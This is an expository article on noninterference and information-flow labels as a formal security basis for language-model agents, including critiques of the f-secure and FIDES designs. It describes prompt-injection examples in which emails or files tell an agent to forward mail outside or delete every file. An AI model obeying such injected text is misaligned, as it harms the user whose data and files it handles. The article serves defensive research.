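# Noninterference as a formal specification for language model agents

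## What noninterference requires, and how an agent is modelled

Noninterference is a property in computer security that limits how one party can affect what another party sees through a system they share. Joseph Goguen and José Meseguer introduced it in 1982. In its usual modern form, it requires two runs of a system to look the same to an observer if their inputs differ only in ways that must not affect what the observer sees. To define an observer, one lists exactly which outputs, calls or times it can see. SRI, whose Computer Science Laboratory developed the theory, credits it with giving a formal basis to military multilevel security, in which people with different clearances use the same machine.

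Noninterference has a new use with language model agents. In these programs, a language model chooses, step by step, which tools to call, such as tools to search a mailbox, send a message or make a payment. An agent holds its user's secrets and also reads text that strangers wrote. Noninterference can express two guarantees that the agent's designers would like to make, that the secrets do not reach the strangers and that the strangers' text does not decide what the agent does.

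### The definition of 1982

Goguen and Meseguer modelled a system as a deterministic state machine. Purdue University's *Noninterference*, a lecture that restates their paper, lists the machine's parts as states, users, commands, and two functions. One function gives the new state after a user issues a command. The other gives the output that a user sees in a state. Users learn about the system only through these outputs.

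Take two groups of users, G and H. Let w be a sequence of commands, each tagged with the user who issued it, and let purge(w) be the same sequence with every command from G deleted. Let view(w) be what the members of H see once the machine has executed w from its initial state. G does not interfere with H when

```
view(w) = view(purge(w))      for every sequence w
```

The equation means that the members of H see exactly what they would have seen if G had never used the machine. Suppose the two groups share a disk. Access control can stop H from opening G's files, but if H can check how much free space remains, the result changes whenever G saves something, and the equation fails.

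The equation compares two runs, and it is equivalent to the more symmetric condition that two command sequences w₁ and w₂ produce the same view whenever they differ only in G's commands. Deleting G's commands from either sequence leaves the same shorter sequence, so by the equation both views equal the view of that shorter sequence. Conversely, setting w₂ = purge(w₁) in the symmetric condition gives back the original equation.

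For programs it is more convenient to vary the starting data than the commands. Smith, in *Principles of Secure Information Flow Analysis*, gives the standard version. Write μ ≈ ν when two memories agree on every public variable, and c(μ) for the memory that program c leaves behind when it starts from μ. Then c satisfies noninterference when

```
μ ≈ ν   implies   c(μ) ≈ c(ν)      for all memories μ and ν
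```

provided both runs finish. That proviso makes the definition termination-insensitive: a secret may still affect whether the program finishes. The version with memories suits agents better than the version with commands. The 1982 model, as the Purdue lecture points out, assumes that the initial state holds nothing sensitive and that secrets arrive through commands, whereas a user's mailbox is full of secrets before the agent takes its first step.

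Whether an agent satisfies noninterference depends on what the observer can see. In *Language-Based Information-Flow Security*, a survey of three decades of work, Sabelfeld and Myers (2003) list several channels besides ordinary output, including whether a program halts, when it acts, and how much memory or power it uses. They argue that a system protects secrets only relative to a model of what attackers observe. A proof that assumes the observer sees only an agent's outgoing messages does not cover an observer who also times them.

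### Why a single trace cannot show a violation

A trace is the sequence of steps and tool calls in one run. Many security rules are conditions on single traces. *Hyperproperties* (Clarkson and Schneider, 2009) gives the example of a rule that forbids a system from writing to the network after reading from a file. Anyone with the log of a run can check whether that run followed the rule. Formally, the rule is a set of permitted traces, and a system obeys it when all of its traces are in the set.

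Noninterference cannot be checked from a single trace. Suppose a log shows an agent reading its user's mailbox and then writing "Tuesday works" to a colleague. If the agent would have written this whatever the mailbox held, nothing has leaked. If a different mailbox would have led it to propose Wednesday, the colleague has learned something about the mail. The log is identical in both cases, so telling them apart requires other traces that show what the agent would have written with different mail.

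Clarkson and Schneider therefore define a *hyperproperty* as a set of sets of traces, which amounts to a set of permitted systems. They write the policy of Goguen and Meseguer as a condition on the whole set T of traces that a deterministic system can produce:

```
for every t in T there is a t' in T such that
    t' contains no secret inputs, and
    t and t' have the same public events
```

Testing an agent for noninterference requires repeating the same tasks with different secrets and comparing the results. A team that attacks an agent a thousand times and finds no stolen data in the logs has not tested noninterference if it skipped that comparison. Enforcement code that monitors a single run has no access to the others, so it has to apply a stricter rule that can be checked within that run, such as a ban on writing to the network after reading a file. That rule blocks harmless messages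 as well as leaks.

Refinement, the practice of turning a loose specification into a program by narrowing its choices, can also break a hyperproperty that the specification satisfies. Clarkson and Schneider describe a system that may output 0, 1 or a secret bit. The set of possible outputs is the same whatever the bit is, so the system satisfies a policy that possible outputs must not depend on secrets. Yet a version that always outputs the secret bit is a legitimate refinement, and it violates the policy. The same can happen with agents. "The model may request any of these tools" is a loose specification, and an actual model narrows it, perhaps according to a secret in its input. For a model that samples its replies, one therefore compares the probabilities of what the observer sees, not only which observations are possible.

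### Labels and how they combine

Nobody can compare all pairs of runs directly, so practical systems attach labels to data, recording how secret each piece is and how far the system trusts it. A theorem then links correct labelling to noninterference. Denning set out the mathematics in *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (1976).

Denning starts from a set of labels and a relation, "may flow to", written ⊑. Most of the other rules follow from consistency. If data may flow from a to b and from b to c, it must be allowed to flow from a to c, because a program can copy it in two steps. If a and b may each flow to c, anything computed from both must also be allowed to flow to c, because a program could copy them there separately and then combine them. So every pair of labels needs a least label to which both may flow. That label is their *join*, written ⊔, and labels ordered in this way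 form a lattice. In practice, combined data takes the stricter label.

For agents, *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) uses a lattice with two independent scales, public to secret and trusted to untrusted, which together give four labels. Public data may flow to secret places and trusted data to untrusted places, but not the reverse.

| Label | Example in an office assistant | May flow to places labelled |
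|---|---|---|
| trusted, public | the user's request | any of the four |
| trusted, secret | a record from the company database | trusted and secret; untrusted and secret |
| untrusted, public | a page from the open web | untrusted and public; untrusted and secret |
| untrusted, secret | a note that combines the record with the web page | untrusted and secret only |

The note in the last row is secret because it could reveal the record, and untrusted because whoever wrote the web page may have shaped it. Real deployments often need finer labels, and Costa and colleagues also describe labels that name the people who may read a document. If A, B and C may read one file and B, C and D may read another, only B and C may read a text derived from both. Integrity labels can name possible writers in the same way, but their join is the union, because any of the four could have contributed to the combined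 text.

### One definition for secrecy and for integrity

So far the forbidden input has mostly been a secret, but the same definition also covers integrity, which requires that untrusted data not affect trusted results. Sabelfeld and Myers credit Kenneth Biba with observing that integrity is the dual of confidentiality, because it keeps information from flowing from the wrong sources rather than to the wrong destinations.

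*The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) expresses both with one parameter, a label n. An observer at n sees exactly the values whose labels may flow to n. Noninterference at n requires that inputs that look alike to this observer lead to results that also look alike to the observer.

If n is "untrusted, public", the observer sees all public data and only secrets can vary unseen, so the requirement is confidentiality. If n is "trusted, secret", the observer sees all trusted data, secret or not, and only untrusted data can vary unseen, so the requirement is integrity. The observer in this second case can be something other than a person, such as the list of payments that an agent makes on its user's authority. That list must stay the same when the agent is run again with a stranger's email worded differently.

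Sabelfeld and Myers also note that the duality between confidentiality and integrity has a limit, because a system can damage integrity by computing the wrong answer, even without outside influence. An agent that misreads its user's request and pays the wrong invoice still satisfies noninterference if it would have made the same mistake whatever strangers had written.

### Explicit and implicit flows

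A label check has to follow two routes by which data can travel. In the examples below, the variable `secret` is secret and the variable `leak` is public. The shorter program contains an *explicit flow*:

```
leak = secret
```

The program copies secret data into a public variable, and a checker that compares the labels on the two sides of the assignment will reject it. The next program contains an *implicit flow*:

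```
leak = 0
if secret % 2 == 1:
    leak = 1
```

Every value assigned here is a constant, so the same checker finds nothing wrong. Yet the program copies the last bit of `secret` into `leak`, because the secret determines whether a step happens. Denning stressed that the information flows even when the assignment does not execute. A reader who finds `leak` still at 0 learns that the secret is even. An agent can leak data in this way without quoting any of it. If it reads a medical record and then books an oncologist rather than a dermatologist, the choice of specialist reveals the diagnosis.

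The remedy is a *program-counter label*, the label of everything that has influenced which step is now executing. Denning attributes the idea to J. S. Fenton, who built it into an abstract computer called the Data Mark Machine. The label begins at the bottom of the lattice. When execution enters a branch, the machine saves the current label and joins to it the label of the tested value. When execution leaves the branch, the machine restores what it saved. Every assignment must then pass this test:

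```
label of the value  ⊔  program-counter label   ⊑   label of the destination
```

Inside the branch above, the constant 1 is public but the program-counter label is secret. Their join is secret, and secret data may not flow into `leak`, so the machine skips the assignment. `leak` now ends at 0 in both runs, whether the secret is odd or even. *A Verified Information-Flow Architecture* (2015) applies the same idea to output by joining the program-counter label onto every number its machine emits. Fenton's argument relies on each variable keeping a fixed label. If variables instead take the label of their current contents, a skipped assignment changes no label, and the leak can return.

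Lowering the label again after the branch is safe only because the next statement executes regardless of the secret's value. If the system cannot establish this, the label has to stay raised for the rest of the run, and more and more data is labelled more strictly than necessary. Sabelfeld and Myers called this *label creep* and considered it the reason purely run-time labelling had proved too restrictive for general use.

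### The agent loop

Most agents share a simple structure, which Costa and colleagues describe as a loop around a growing conversation:

```
history = [developer's instructions, user's task]
repeat:
    reply = model(history)
    if reply requests a tool call:
        result = run the requested tool
        history = history + [reply, result]
    else:
        return reply to the user
```

The model only produces text. When part of that text is formatted as a tool call, with a tool's name and arguments, the surrounding code detects the call and determines whether to run it. Tools read and change a store of data outside the conversation, such as a mailbox, a calendar or a bank account. The *planner* is the model together with the code that chooses the next step. A *monitor* is trusted code that sits between the planner and the tools and allows or refuses each call.

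Adding labels changes little in this structure. In the scheme of Costa and colleagues, each message has a label, and the conversation's *context label* is the join of all its messages' labels. A reply from the model takes the context label of the conversation that produced it. The monitor checks the labels on a requested call against a policy, and the tool's result is labelled with the join of the call's labels and those of any data the tool read. In their example policies, a consequential call may proceed only if its label is trusted, and a call that sends information out may proceed only if every recipient has permission to read that information.

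The context label serves the same role as the program-counter label in an ordinary program, because the model's reply selects the next step. When the reply is itself code, Garby and colleagues execute that code under a program-counter label equal to the conversation's label.

### Prompt injection

Tool results enter the conversation as text, next to the user's instructions. Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues (2024) argue in *AgentDojo* that this makes agents vulnerable, because language models operate directly on text and lack a formal way to distinguish instructions from data. In a *prompt injection* attack, someone places instructions in material that the agent will read, and the model acts on them. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026) defines the attack as indirect when the instructions are in content that the agent retrieves. Costa and colleagues give the example of a user who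 asks an agent to summarize recent emails about a project and send the summary to a manager. One of the emails contains text instructing the agent to ignore its instructions and forward the top message in the mailbox to an outside address.

Filters that look for suspicious wording give no guarantee. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* notes that adaptive attacks can bypass defences tuned to fixed templates. Designers also cannot simply forbid agents to take guidance from what they read. In *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing*, Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues (2025) describe an agent that is asked to summarise an issue in a software tracker, finds that it depends on another issue, and decides to summarise both. Text from the tracker changed what the agent did, but nobody would call that an attack. In their view, this differs from an injection in where the text came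 from and how much it changed. Dongol (2026), in *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, concludes that noninterference is too strong for a useful agent.

A label records only a text's origin, regardless of whether the text looks malicious. In the email example, the user's request is trusted and public, while the emails are untrusted and secret. Once the emails enter the conversation, the join of all its labels is untrusted and secret, and every later reply gets that label. A monitor that permits consequential calls only with a trusted label will block a call that forwards mail to the attacker. It will also block the call that sends the manager the summary the user asked for, because both calls have the same label.

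A model computes its reply from its entire input, with no assignments or branches in between for a label tracker to follow, so any message could have affected the reply. Giving the reply the join of all the messages' labels is certainly sound, though some researchers try to estimate which messages had an influence and use only their labels. The email stays in the history, so the label does not come down again. An agent can reach with one tool call a label that an ordinary program would reach only after many steps of label creep.

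### Keeping untrusted text away from the planner

The obvious solution is to keep the email out of the planner's conversation. *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) proposes doing this with two models. A privileged model plans and requests tool calls but never sees untrusted text. A *quarantined model* reads untrusted text and returns values but has no tools. Ordinary code, called the controller, connects them.

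Suppose the user wants a summary of the latest email. The privileged model requests the email, and the controller fetches it, stores it under a name such as `$VAR1`, and returns only the name. The privileged model then requests a summary of `$VAR1`. The controller passes the email's text to the quarantined model and stores the summary as `$VAR2`. The privileged model then instructs the controller to display `$VAR2`, without ever receiving its contents. Willison allows one exception, which is that an answer from a fixed set of categories may go back to the privileged model after the controller has checked it.

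The planner's context and its choice of tools stay labelled as trusted. The contents of `$VAR2` remain untrusted, and an attacker who wrote the email can still slant the summary. Willison warned that the pattern made assistants harder to build and less pleasant to use, and that a single mistake letting untrusted text through to the privileged model would undo the protection. The planner also cannot read untrusted content, so it cannot plan how to complete whatever tasks are due today if that content is where the tasks are listed. Later systems nonetheless built on the pattern, including, as Willison noted in 2025, CaMeL, an agent design from Google DeepMind.

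### What AgentDojo measures

Comparing such designs requires a common set of tasks, and most work on agents and information flow uses AgentDojo. Debenedetti and colleagues built it from four simulated environments: an office workspace, the messaging service Slack, a travel agency and a bank. The environments contain 97 user tasks, such as paying a bill or booking a hotel, and 27 attacker goals. Pairing every user task with every attacker goal from the same environment yields 629 security cases. Code inspects the agent's output and the state of the environment to decide whether the user's task was completed and whether the attack succeeded. Debenedetti and colleagues avoided using a language model as judge because an injection might fool it too.

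The benchmark reports three figures. *Benign utility* is the share of user tasks that the agent solves when nobody attacks it. *Utility under attack* is the share of security cases in which it solves the user's task without harmful side effects. The *targeted attack success rate* is the share of security cases in which the agent does what the attacker wanted. Comparing benign utility with and without a defence shows how much the defence reduces the share of tasks completed, which has to be measured because no theorem provides it.

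Attack success rates call for more caution because each security case checks a single run for one particular outcome. An agent can have a rate of zero and still let a stranger's email influence its actions in ways nobody listed as an attack goal. The rate also depends on the strength of the attack. AgentDojo's built-in attack is a fixed message claiming that the attacker's task must come first. *AutoDojo* (2026) compares this baseline with injections that another language model improves over several rounds.

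### A program that the model chooses as it runs

Classical work on information flow starts from the text of a program. *Certification of Programs for Secure Information Flow* (Denning and Denning, 1977) presents a check simple enough for most compilers of the time to include. For a conditional statement, the compiler collects every variable that any branch could assign and verifies that the label of the condition may flow to each of them. Because the compiler has the text of every branch, it does not need to know which one will execute, and it can certify a program that passes as secure before it runs.

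A compiler cannot analyse an agent in the same way because, as Christodorescu and colleagues observe, an agent has no fixed program and in effect composes many programs as it goes. The branch not taken causes the most trouble, since it can be inspected in ordinary code but exists in an agent only as the reply that the model would have given to a different conversation. Training the model to behave does not solve the problem either. Christodorescu and colleagues point out that training a model never to do something makes it likely to comply on some inputs but does not guarantee that it will comply on all of them.

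A noninterference proof can succeed without assuming anything about the model's judgement, because it compares two runs of the same model. As long as the two conversations are identical, a deterministic model gives identical replies, and a sampled model draws its replies from the same distribution, however easily it is misled. The proof then depends only on controlling what enters the conversation. Once the conversations differ in forbidden data, the replies may differ in any way, and the proof has to treat every step they select as something the observer must not see.

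Garby and colleagues build on this reasoning by proving noninterference for every program in a small language, including programs that the model writes during the run, so the guarantee holds whichever program the model picks. Costa and colleagues instead keep a fixed loop and enforce security with a monitor around the model. Such a monitor observes only the current run, so to guarantee noninterference it would have to block any visible call that forbidden data might have prompted, including calls that the agent would have made without that data.

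## f-secure: a planner that never reads untrusted text

It is easier to block every call that an attacker's text might have prompted if that text never reaches the planner. Wu, Cecchetti and Xiao (2024), in *System-Level Defense against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks*, built an agent called f-secure on this idea and set out to prove noninterference for it, an early attempt at such a proof for an agent with a language model as planner. The system is now mainly of historical interest. The evaluation of *Trident* (2026), a later design, runs three rival defences but includes f-secure only in a table of features. The theorem is still worth studying closely because the argument is short and later designs have had to deal with a gap in it.

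### Probabilistic noninterference

Goguen and Meseguer's machine was deterministic. Researchers first extended noninterference to nondeterministic systems by comparing which outputs were possible in each run. Gray (1990), in *Probabilistic Interference*, compared the probabilities of outputs instead. A longer report for the US Naval Research Laboratory, Gray (1991), shows why with a machine that accepts secret inputs of 0 or 1, remembers the latest one, and prints a public digit that matches it 95% of the time.

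The machine can print either digit whatever the secret is, so it passes restrictiveness, then the leading test for nondeterministic systems. Yet anyone who reads one digit can guess the secret correctly 95% of the time. Printing does not change the machine's state, so an observer who waits for three digits and takes the majority is right more than 99% of the time.

Gray's stricter test compares states that look the same to the observer. Each visible event must have the same probability in all of them, and must lead with that probability to states that again look the same. *HyperPCTL* (2018) presents a logic for such properties and gives the general form, *probabilistic noninterference*. It requires every observable pattern to have the same probability from any two starting states that look alike to the observer.

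A language model that samples its replies is an extreme case of Gray's machine. Unless the surrounding code excludes unlikely words, every word has a nonzero probability, so almost any reply is possible after any conversation. A test that checks only which replies are possible would therefore pass an agent that obeys an injected instruction 99% of the time.

### The property claimed for f-secure

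Wu and colleagues write Q for all the information an agent could read while it handles a query q, and π for the trace. Two information sets are equivalent, Q₁ ≃ Q₂, when they contain the same trusted items. Their untrusted items may differ in any way. Definition 6.1 in the paper, *execution trace non-compromise*, then requires

```
Q₁ ≃ Q₂   implies   Pr[π | q, Q₁] = Pr[π | q, Q₂]      for every query q and trace π
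```

The f-secure guarantee is probabilistic noninterference for integrity, with an observer who sees the sequence of steps. Each step names a tool and its inputs. An input can be a reference to an earlier result, and the observer sees the reference but not the data behind it. So if an attacker changes the wording of a summary that the agent emails to someone, the runs with and without the change still count as the same.

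Noninterference is demanding. *PACE* (2026), a later defence for tool-using agents, uses probabilistic noninterference as a standard for comparison but does not claim to satisfy it.

### From a request to a step

f-secure consists of a planner, an executor made of ordinary code, and a monitor. The planner writes one step at a time in a fixed format with five fields: a number, an instruction in words, the tool or model to call, its input, and a description of the expected output. If step 2 needs the result of step 1, the planner writes the reference `{Data_output:1}`. The monitor then loads the data behind it, and the executor passes that data to the tool or model. A step may also call a fresh language model, for instance to summarise a document. That model serves as a quarantined model.

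Before each planning call, the monitor checks each item in the earlier results and loads only the trusted ones into the planner's prompt. In one of the paper's case studies, a user asks the agent to read emails about budgets and notify the manager if any budget exceeds $1,000. The search returns three emails. The monitor passes the planner the two from colleagues, which give budgets of $724 and $1,024, and withholds the third, which is from an attacker called Mallory. When a result contains nothing trusted, the planner gets only the reference.

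Every new step then receives a label:

```
label(sᵢ) = label of the prompt  ⊔  labels of the earlier steps
                                 ⊔  labels of the results loaded for planning
```

The monitor checks the step's syntax and passes the step to the executor. The result's label is the join of its inputs' labels. If the step succeeds, the monitor stores the result and adds the step to the trace, and the planner writes the next step. The cycle ends when the planner issues an end signal.

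### The proof by induction

Theorem 6.2 in the paper states that f-secure satisfies the definition. The proof compares what the planner receives in two runs with equivalent information sets.

At step 1, the planner receives a trusted template and the user's query, which are the same in both runs. Now suppose that the first i − 1 steps and their trusted results agree. The monitor then loads the same items into the prompt for step i. Anything computed from untrusted data has an untrusted label, so the monitor leaves it out. The planner's entire input is therefore identical in the two runs, and the same model with the same input draws its next step from the same distribution. The probability of the whole trace is a product of these conditional probabilities:

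```
Pr[π | q, Q] = Pr[s₁ | q] × Pr[s₂ | q, s₁, trusted part of o₁] × ...
```

Here o₁ is the result of step 1. Every factor is the same under Q₁ and Q₂, so the products are equal. If a trusted result is random, it has the same distribution in both runs, and averaging over it preserves the equality.

This proof, like others that compare two runs of the same model, relies on no assumption about how well the model resists injections, so the same proof applies if the model is replaced.

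In an example based on another of the paper's case studies, a user asks the agent to read `report.txt`, send it to Alice, and then delete it. The file is untrusted, and its malicious version contains an instruction to delete every file in the folder. The table illustrates the property with invented, rounded probabilities for what the agent does after opening the file.

| Rest of the trace | f-secure, either version | Planner reads the harmless version | Planner reads the malicious version |
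|---|---|---|---|
| send the text, delete the file | 0.80 | 0.80 | 0.30 |
| summarise the text, send the summary, delete the file | 0.15 | 0.15 | 0.05 |
| delete the file without sending anything | 0.05 | 0.05 | 0.05 |
| delete every file | 0.00 | 0.00 | 0.60 |

The planner in f-secure never reads the file, so its outputs have the same distribution for both versions. It still makes a mistake in one run out of twenty, but the attacker cannot change that rate. If the planner did read the file, the distribution would shift and noninterference would fail.

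### When a step fails

If a step fails, the monitor calls the planner again with the same inputs, and the failed step does not enter the trace. Untrusted content can affect whether a step fails.

Suppose the report's author makes it so long that the mail tool always rejects the full text. The planner's input stays the same, so each retry follows the same probabilities, but only a successful step counts. The retries continue until the planner draws one of the other two options. Their probabilities of 0.15 and 0.05 rescale to 0.75 and 0.25, so the agent now deletes the report unsent in one run out of four instead of one in twenty. The short and long versions of the file differ only in untrusted content, so Definition 6.1 does not hold.

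A planner that always picks its most likely reply would propose the same failing step until it reached the step limit. The file's author would then control whether the task finishes. CaMeL, a later design that also retries after errors, has a related leak.

The proof in the paper's Appendix A covers the planning and execution of a step but omits the branch for failures. For execution, Wu and colleagues correctly argue that only the monitor can modify the trace and that no tool or model can call the monitor. But the monitor adds a step to the trace only if the step succeeded, and untrusted content can determine whether it does. Theorem 6.2 therefore implicitly assumes that the success of a step does not depend on untrusted information. The paper's threat model excludes attacks on the availability of tools and models, an exclusion that may have been meant to cover such failures, but neither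 the definition nor the theorem includes it. The retry after a syntax error causes no such problem, because the syntax check depends only on the step, which the planner wrote from trusted data.

The labels that f-secure assigns to tool results depend on a similar assumption. Its tool for merging two files returns only a message of success or failure, which Wu and colleagues label as trusted. Their code opens both files as text and reports failure on any error. An attacker who controls an untrusted file could therefore choose which message the planner reads by including or omitting bytes that are not valid text.

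The email search has a subtler version of the problem. In the budget case, it fetches the three newest emails and labels each by its sender. Two more emails from Mallory would push the older of the colleagues' emails, which gives the $1,024 budget, out of the results. The planner would receive only $724 and have no reason to notify the manager, although it had read nothing that Mallory wrote. *Trident* avoids this by treating even the sender's address in a search result as untrusted if the text of other emails could have affected which email the search returned.

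Later designs handle the failure signal explicitly. In *Trident*, whenever the outcome of an action might depend on hidden data, reporting success or failure to the planner uses one bit of a budget set in advance. If the budget is zero, the monitor refuses such actions before trying them, and the distribution of traces is the same whatever the attacker writes. This corollary is close to what Wu and colleagues wanted to prove. Its proof has been checked in Lean, a proof assistant. It assumes, among other things, that every tool call succeeds if the monitor admits it.

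*Kaer* (Mallick, Rose and colleagues, 2026) limits the signal in another way. A central planner assigns subtasks to other agents, some of which may be malicious. An agent that fails must pick its reason from a fixed list, and the planner receives only the matching template. A malicious agent can still affect the new plan through the reason it picks, but it cannot write any text the planner reads.

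The agent could also end the run at the first failure. Untrusted data would then affect only whether the run finishes, which a termination-insensitive version of probabilistic noninterference allows, but the agent could not recover from ordinary errors.

### Attacks stopped and tasks completed

Wu and colleagues tested f-secure on InjecAgent, a benchmark of 1,054 cases in which a tool's result contains an injected instruction. An ordinary agent loop with GPT-4 Turbo followed the instruction in 28.7% of cases, and in 44.5% when the attack used stronger wording. With f-secure the rate was zero for all four models tested. Because the researchers had labelled every tool result as untrusted, the planner never received an injection, and a nonzero rate would have indicated a bug.

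The evaluation on ordinary tasks used three benchmarks in which an agent types strings letter by letter or looks up facts in linked tables. With GPT-4 Turbo, f-secure solved every typing task and 95% of the table tasks, while the ordinary loop solved 90% of the table tasks. With the weaker GPT-3.5 Turbo, f-secure solved 60% of the tasks on one typing benchmark, compared with 80% for the ordinary loop, but did better than the loop on the other. The monitor took less than a millisecond per step, while the model took one to three seconds to write the step.

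In these tests, however, the researchers labelled every tool result as trusted, so the monitor had nothing to withhold. The results suggest that the fixed step format does little harm and sometimes helps. They do not measure how much the guarantee reduces task performance, because the security tests and the task tests used opposite labels.

*Prompt Flow Integrity to Prevent Privilege Escalation in LLM Agents* (2025) gives an outside estimate of f-secure's performance. Its authors approximated f-secure by switching off parts of their own system, then counted the tasks an agent completed while resisting attack. On a modified AgentDojo, the approximation succeeded on 40% of tasks, compared with 12% for an undefended agent. On 19 tasks that use shell commands, it succeeded on two and the undefended agent on none.

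Part of the shortfall comes from attacks that f-secure was not designed to stop. An attack counts as successful if false data, such as a phishing link, ends up in a sensitive call. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) points out that isolating the planner fixes which calls run and in what order, but not the data in them. For example, an f-secure planner could set a payment's recipient to a reference to a stranger's invoice. The trace would then be the same whichever account the invoice named.

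The rest of the shortfall comes from tasks in which untrusted text has to determine the next step. Willison's pattern has the same limit, but f-secure is stricter and can't even handle "book a table if the website says the restaurant is open". A quarantined model can read the website and answer yes or no, but its answer inherits the website's untrusted label, and f-secure lacks Willison's exception for fixed categories.

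The user can get around this only by marking a source as trusted in advance. That lets in everything from the source, including a stranger's text that a trusted colleague has forwarded. *Trident* reports that only 20 of AgentDojo's 97 user tasks have a plan that depends on what the agent reads, so this limitation counts for little in AgentDojo scores.

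## FIDES: why secrets are allowed to influence which tool is called

Some tasks require the planner to read untrusted text before it can choose the next step. FIDES, which Costa and colleagues designed at Microsoft in 2025, lets the planner choose whether to read a result or leave it hidden. Reading it makes the context label stricter, and the monitor then blocks some tools. For secrets, FIDES enforces only *explicit secrecy*, a property weaker than noninterference. It forbids copying secret data into public places but lets a secret influence which tools the agent calls and in what order.

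### Two policies and what each leaves open

FIDES refines the labelled agent loop by giving each tool call one label for the decision to make the call and a separate label for each argument. The monitor checks these labels against the two example policies of Costa and colleagues, which Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) call *trusted action* and *permitted flow* in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*. Trusted action requires that, for consequential calls, both the decision to make the call and the arguments that matter be trusted. Permitted flow requires that every recipient of outgoing data have permission to read it.

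Permitted flow alone does not stop prompt injection. Text in an email can still make the agent send a message, although the message can contain only data that its recipients are allowed to read. Trusted action alone lets the agent send out secrets if the decision to send them came from a trusted context. Costa and colleagues describe this as a form of *robust declassification*, meaning that a user can deliberately release a secret but a stranger's text cannot trigger the release. The monitor cannot distinguish a deliberate release from a mistake by the model, so the policy depends on the planner interpreting the user's request correctly.

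### Hiding only what would raise the label

In the basic loop, an agent that summarises emails for a manager cannot send the summary, because the emails have made its context untrusted. FIDES compares the label of each part of a tool's result with the context label. If a part has a stricter label, the surrounding code stores it in a variable and shows the planner only the variable's name. For an email, the planner might see a trusted date next to names that stand for the subject and body. It can then finish the task in three calls:

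```
read_emails(number=3)
query_llm(prompt="Summarize ...", input=#read_emails_0)
send_message(to=manager, message=#query_llm_0)
```

As in Willison's pattern, a quarantined model writes the summary, which stays in a variable. The decision to send the message and the choice of recipient are therefore trusted. Only the message's content is untrusted, and the policy can allow that.

Unlike f-secure, FIDES has an `inspect` tool, which puts a variable's contents into the conversation and raises the context label for the rest of the run. The planner can also have the quarantined model reduce a text to a yes or no and inspect only that answer, which limits how much an attacker can convey.

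### Explicit secrecy and the leak it permits

Daniel Schoepe and colleagues defined explicit secrecy in 2016 for software that tracks labelled data through ordinary programs. Costa and colleagues adapt it to agents. Let c be the planner's state together with the latest message, and let d be the datastore that the tools read and change. Part or all of a run has some combined effect g on the datastore. This g is a function that repeats the run's tool calls, with the same arguments, on any datastore one applies it to. Write d₁ ≈ d₂ when two datastores agree on every public variable. Then c satisfies explicit secrecy when

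```
d₁ ≈ d₂   implies   g(d₁) ≈ g(d₂)      for all d₁, d₂ and every effect g of a run from (c, d₁)
```

Under noninterference, the agent would choose its calls again when it starts from datastore d₂. Explicit secrecy instead applies the calls from the d₁ run to both datastores, so it does not cover anything an observer could learn from the choice of calls.

Suppose a user asks an agent to post two web pages, A and B, on a public board, with A first if a medical test came back positive. The pages sit in variables with public labels. The planner inspects the test result, which makes its context secret, and then posts the pages:

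```
positive:   post(A), post(B)      the board shows A, B
negative:   post(B), post(A)      the board shows B, A
```

Permitted flow allows all of these calls because their content is public. Explicit secrecy also holds, because the calls in the upper line produce the board A, B whichever result the datastore contains. Noninterference fails because anyone who knows the instruction can infer the test result from the board.

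Taken literally, the definition permits much more than this. Suppose the agent reads a diagnosis and types it into a public post. The diagnosis is now part of an argument, which g repeats unchanged. When g runs on a datastore with a different diagnosis, it still posts the original one, so the public parts agree and the definition holds. The definition rules out only calls that move secrets within the datastore, such as one that copies a medical file into a public folder. Ordinary programs avoid this problem because their text contains no secrets, but an agent's conversation can contain many. The monitor is stricter than the definition here. The diagnosis makes the context secret, any argument the planner then writes inherits that label, and permitted flow blocks the post.

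Costa and colleagues chose explicit secrecy because they considered noninterference too restrictive. In their view, it would essentially forbid any call that may write to a public place after any call that may read a secret. That is accurate for the basic loop, where every result enters the conversation, but noninterference is less restrictive for a planner that can hide results. If a secret stays in a variable that the planner never inspects, the planner's conversation is the same in both runs, and so are its later public calls. Wu and colleagues used this argument for f-secure, and it has the same weakness here when hidden data can make a call fail. In their tests, however, Costa and colleagues hid results based only on their integrity labels, so trusted secrets went straight into the conversation.

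### What the formal claim covers

The explicit secrecy claim applies to the labelled planning loop with a deterministic model, which always gives the same reply to the same conversation. It does not cover models that sample their replies, or side channels such as timing and network packet length. The loop in the formal model stops at the first policy violation, whereas the agents in the experiments received a message about the blocked call and continued. Costa and colleagues define the property in detail but do not write out a proof that the loop satisfies it.

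Versions of the paper differ on whether they claim noninterference for integrity, and the version that presents explicit secrecy as its security guarantee does not. Its conclusion lists integrity among the properties that label tracking can enforce, but it has no theorem showing this.

The basic loop does satisfy noninterference for integrity if the labels are correct and the trusted-action policy applies, without exception, to every consequential call and all its arguments. The observer here sees only the consequential calls that run. If two runs differ only in untrusted data, their conversations are identical until an untrusted result arrives, so a deterministic model requests the same calls in both up to that point. After that, the context stays untrusted and the monitor blocks every further consequential call. The observer therefore sees the same list of calls in both runs. If the model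 samples its replies, the lists have the same distribution.

Hidden variables let the planner keep making consequential calls after a tool has fetched untrusted data, so the labels matter more. In the experiments, Costa and colleagues labelled the fields of each email separately. The planner could still see how many emails a search had returned, and a stranger can change that number by sending an email.

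### Data-independent and data-dependent tasks

Costa and colleagues describe a task by the datastores it may start from and, for each datastore d, the set of correct traces, written ⟦t⟧d. A trace here consists of tool calls and a final response. The task is *data-independent* if some trace is correct for every datastore:

```
⋂ ⟦t⟧d  ≠  ∅      taken over all datastores d
```

A task is data-independent if the same tool calls work whatever the data, and *data-dependent* otherwise. In the FIDES paper's examples, an argument that the planner passes by reference counts as the same argument whatever it contains. Sending a summary of three emails to a colleague is therefore data-independent, because the same three calls work for any emails. Checking the emails for a meeting invitation and creating a calendar event if there is one is data-dependent, because the correct calls differ between mailboxes.

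Whether a data-dependent task conflicts with noninterference depends on the observer. If only the user can read the calendar, an outsider sees the same thing whether or not the agent adds an event, so the emails remain confidential. For integrity, the observer is the calendar, and the conflict is unavoidable. Strangers may have written the emails, and the user has asked for the text of those emails to determine what appears in the calendar.

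### Why usefulness and noninterference conflict

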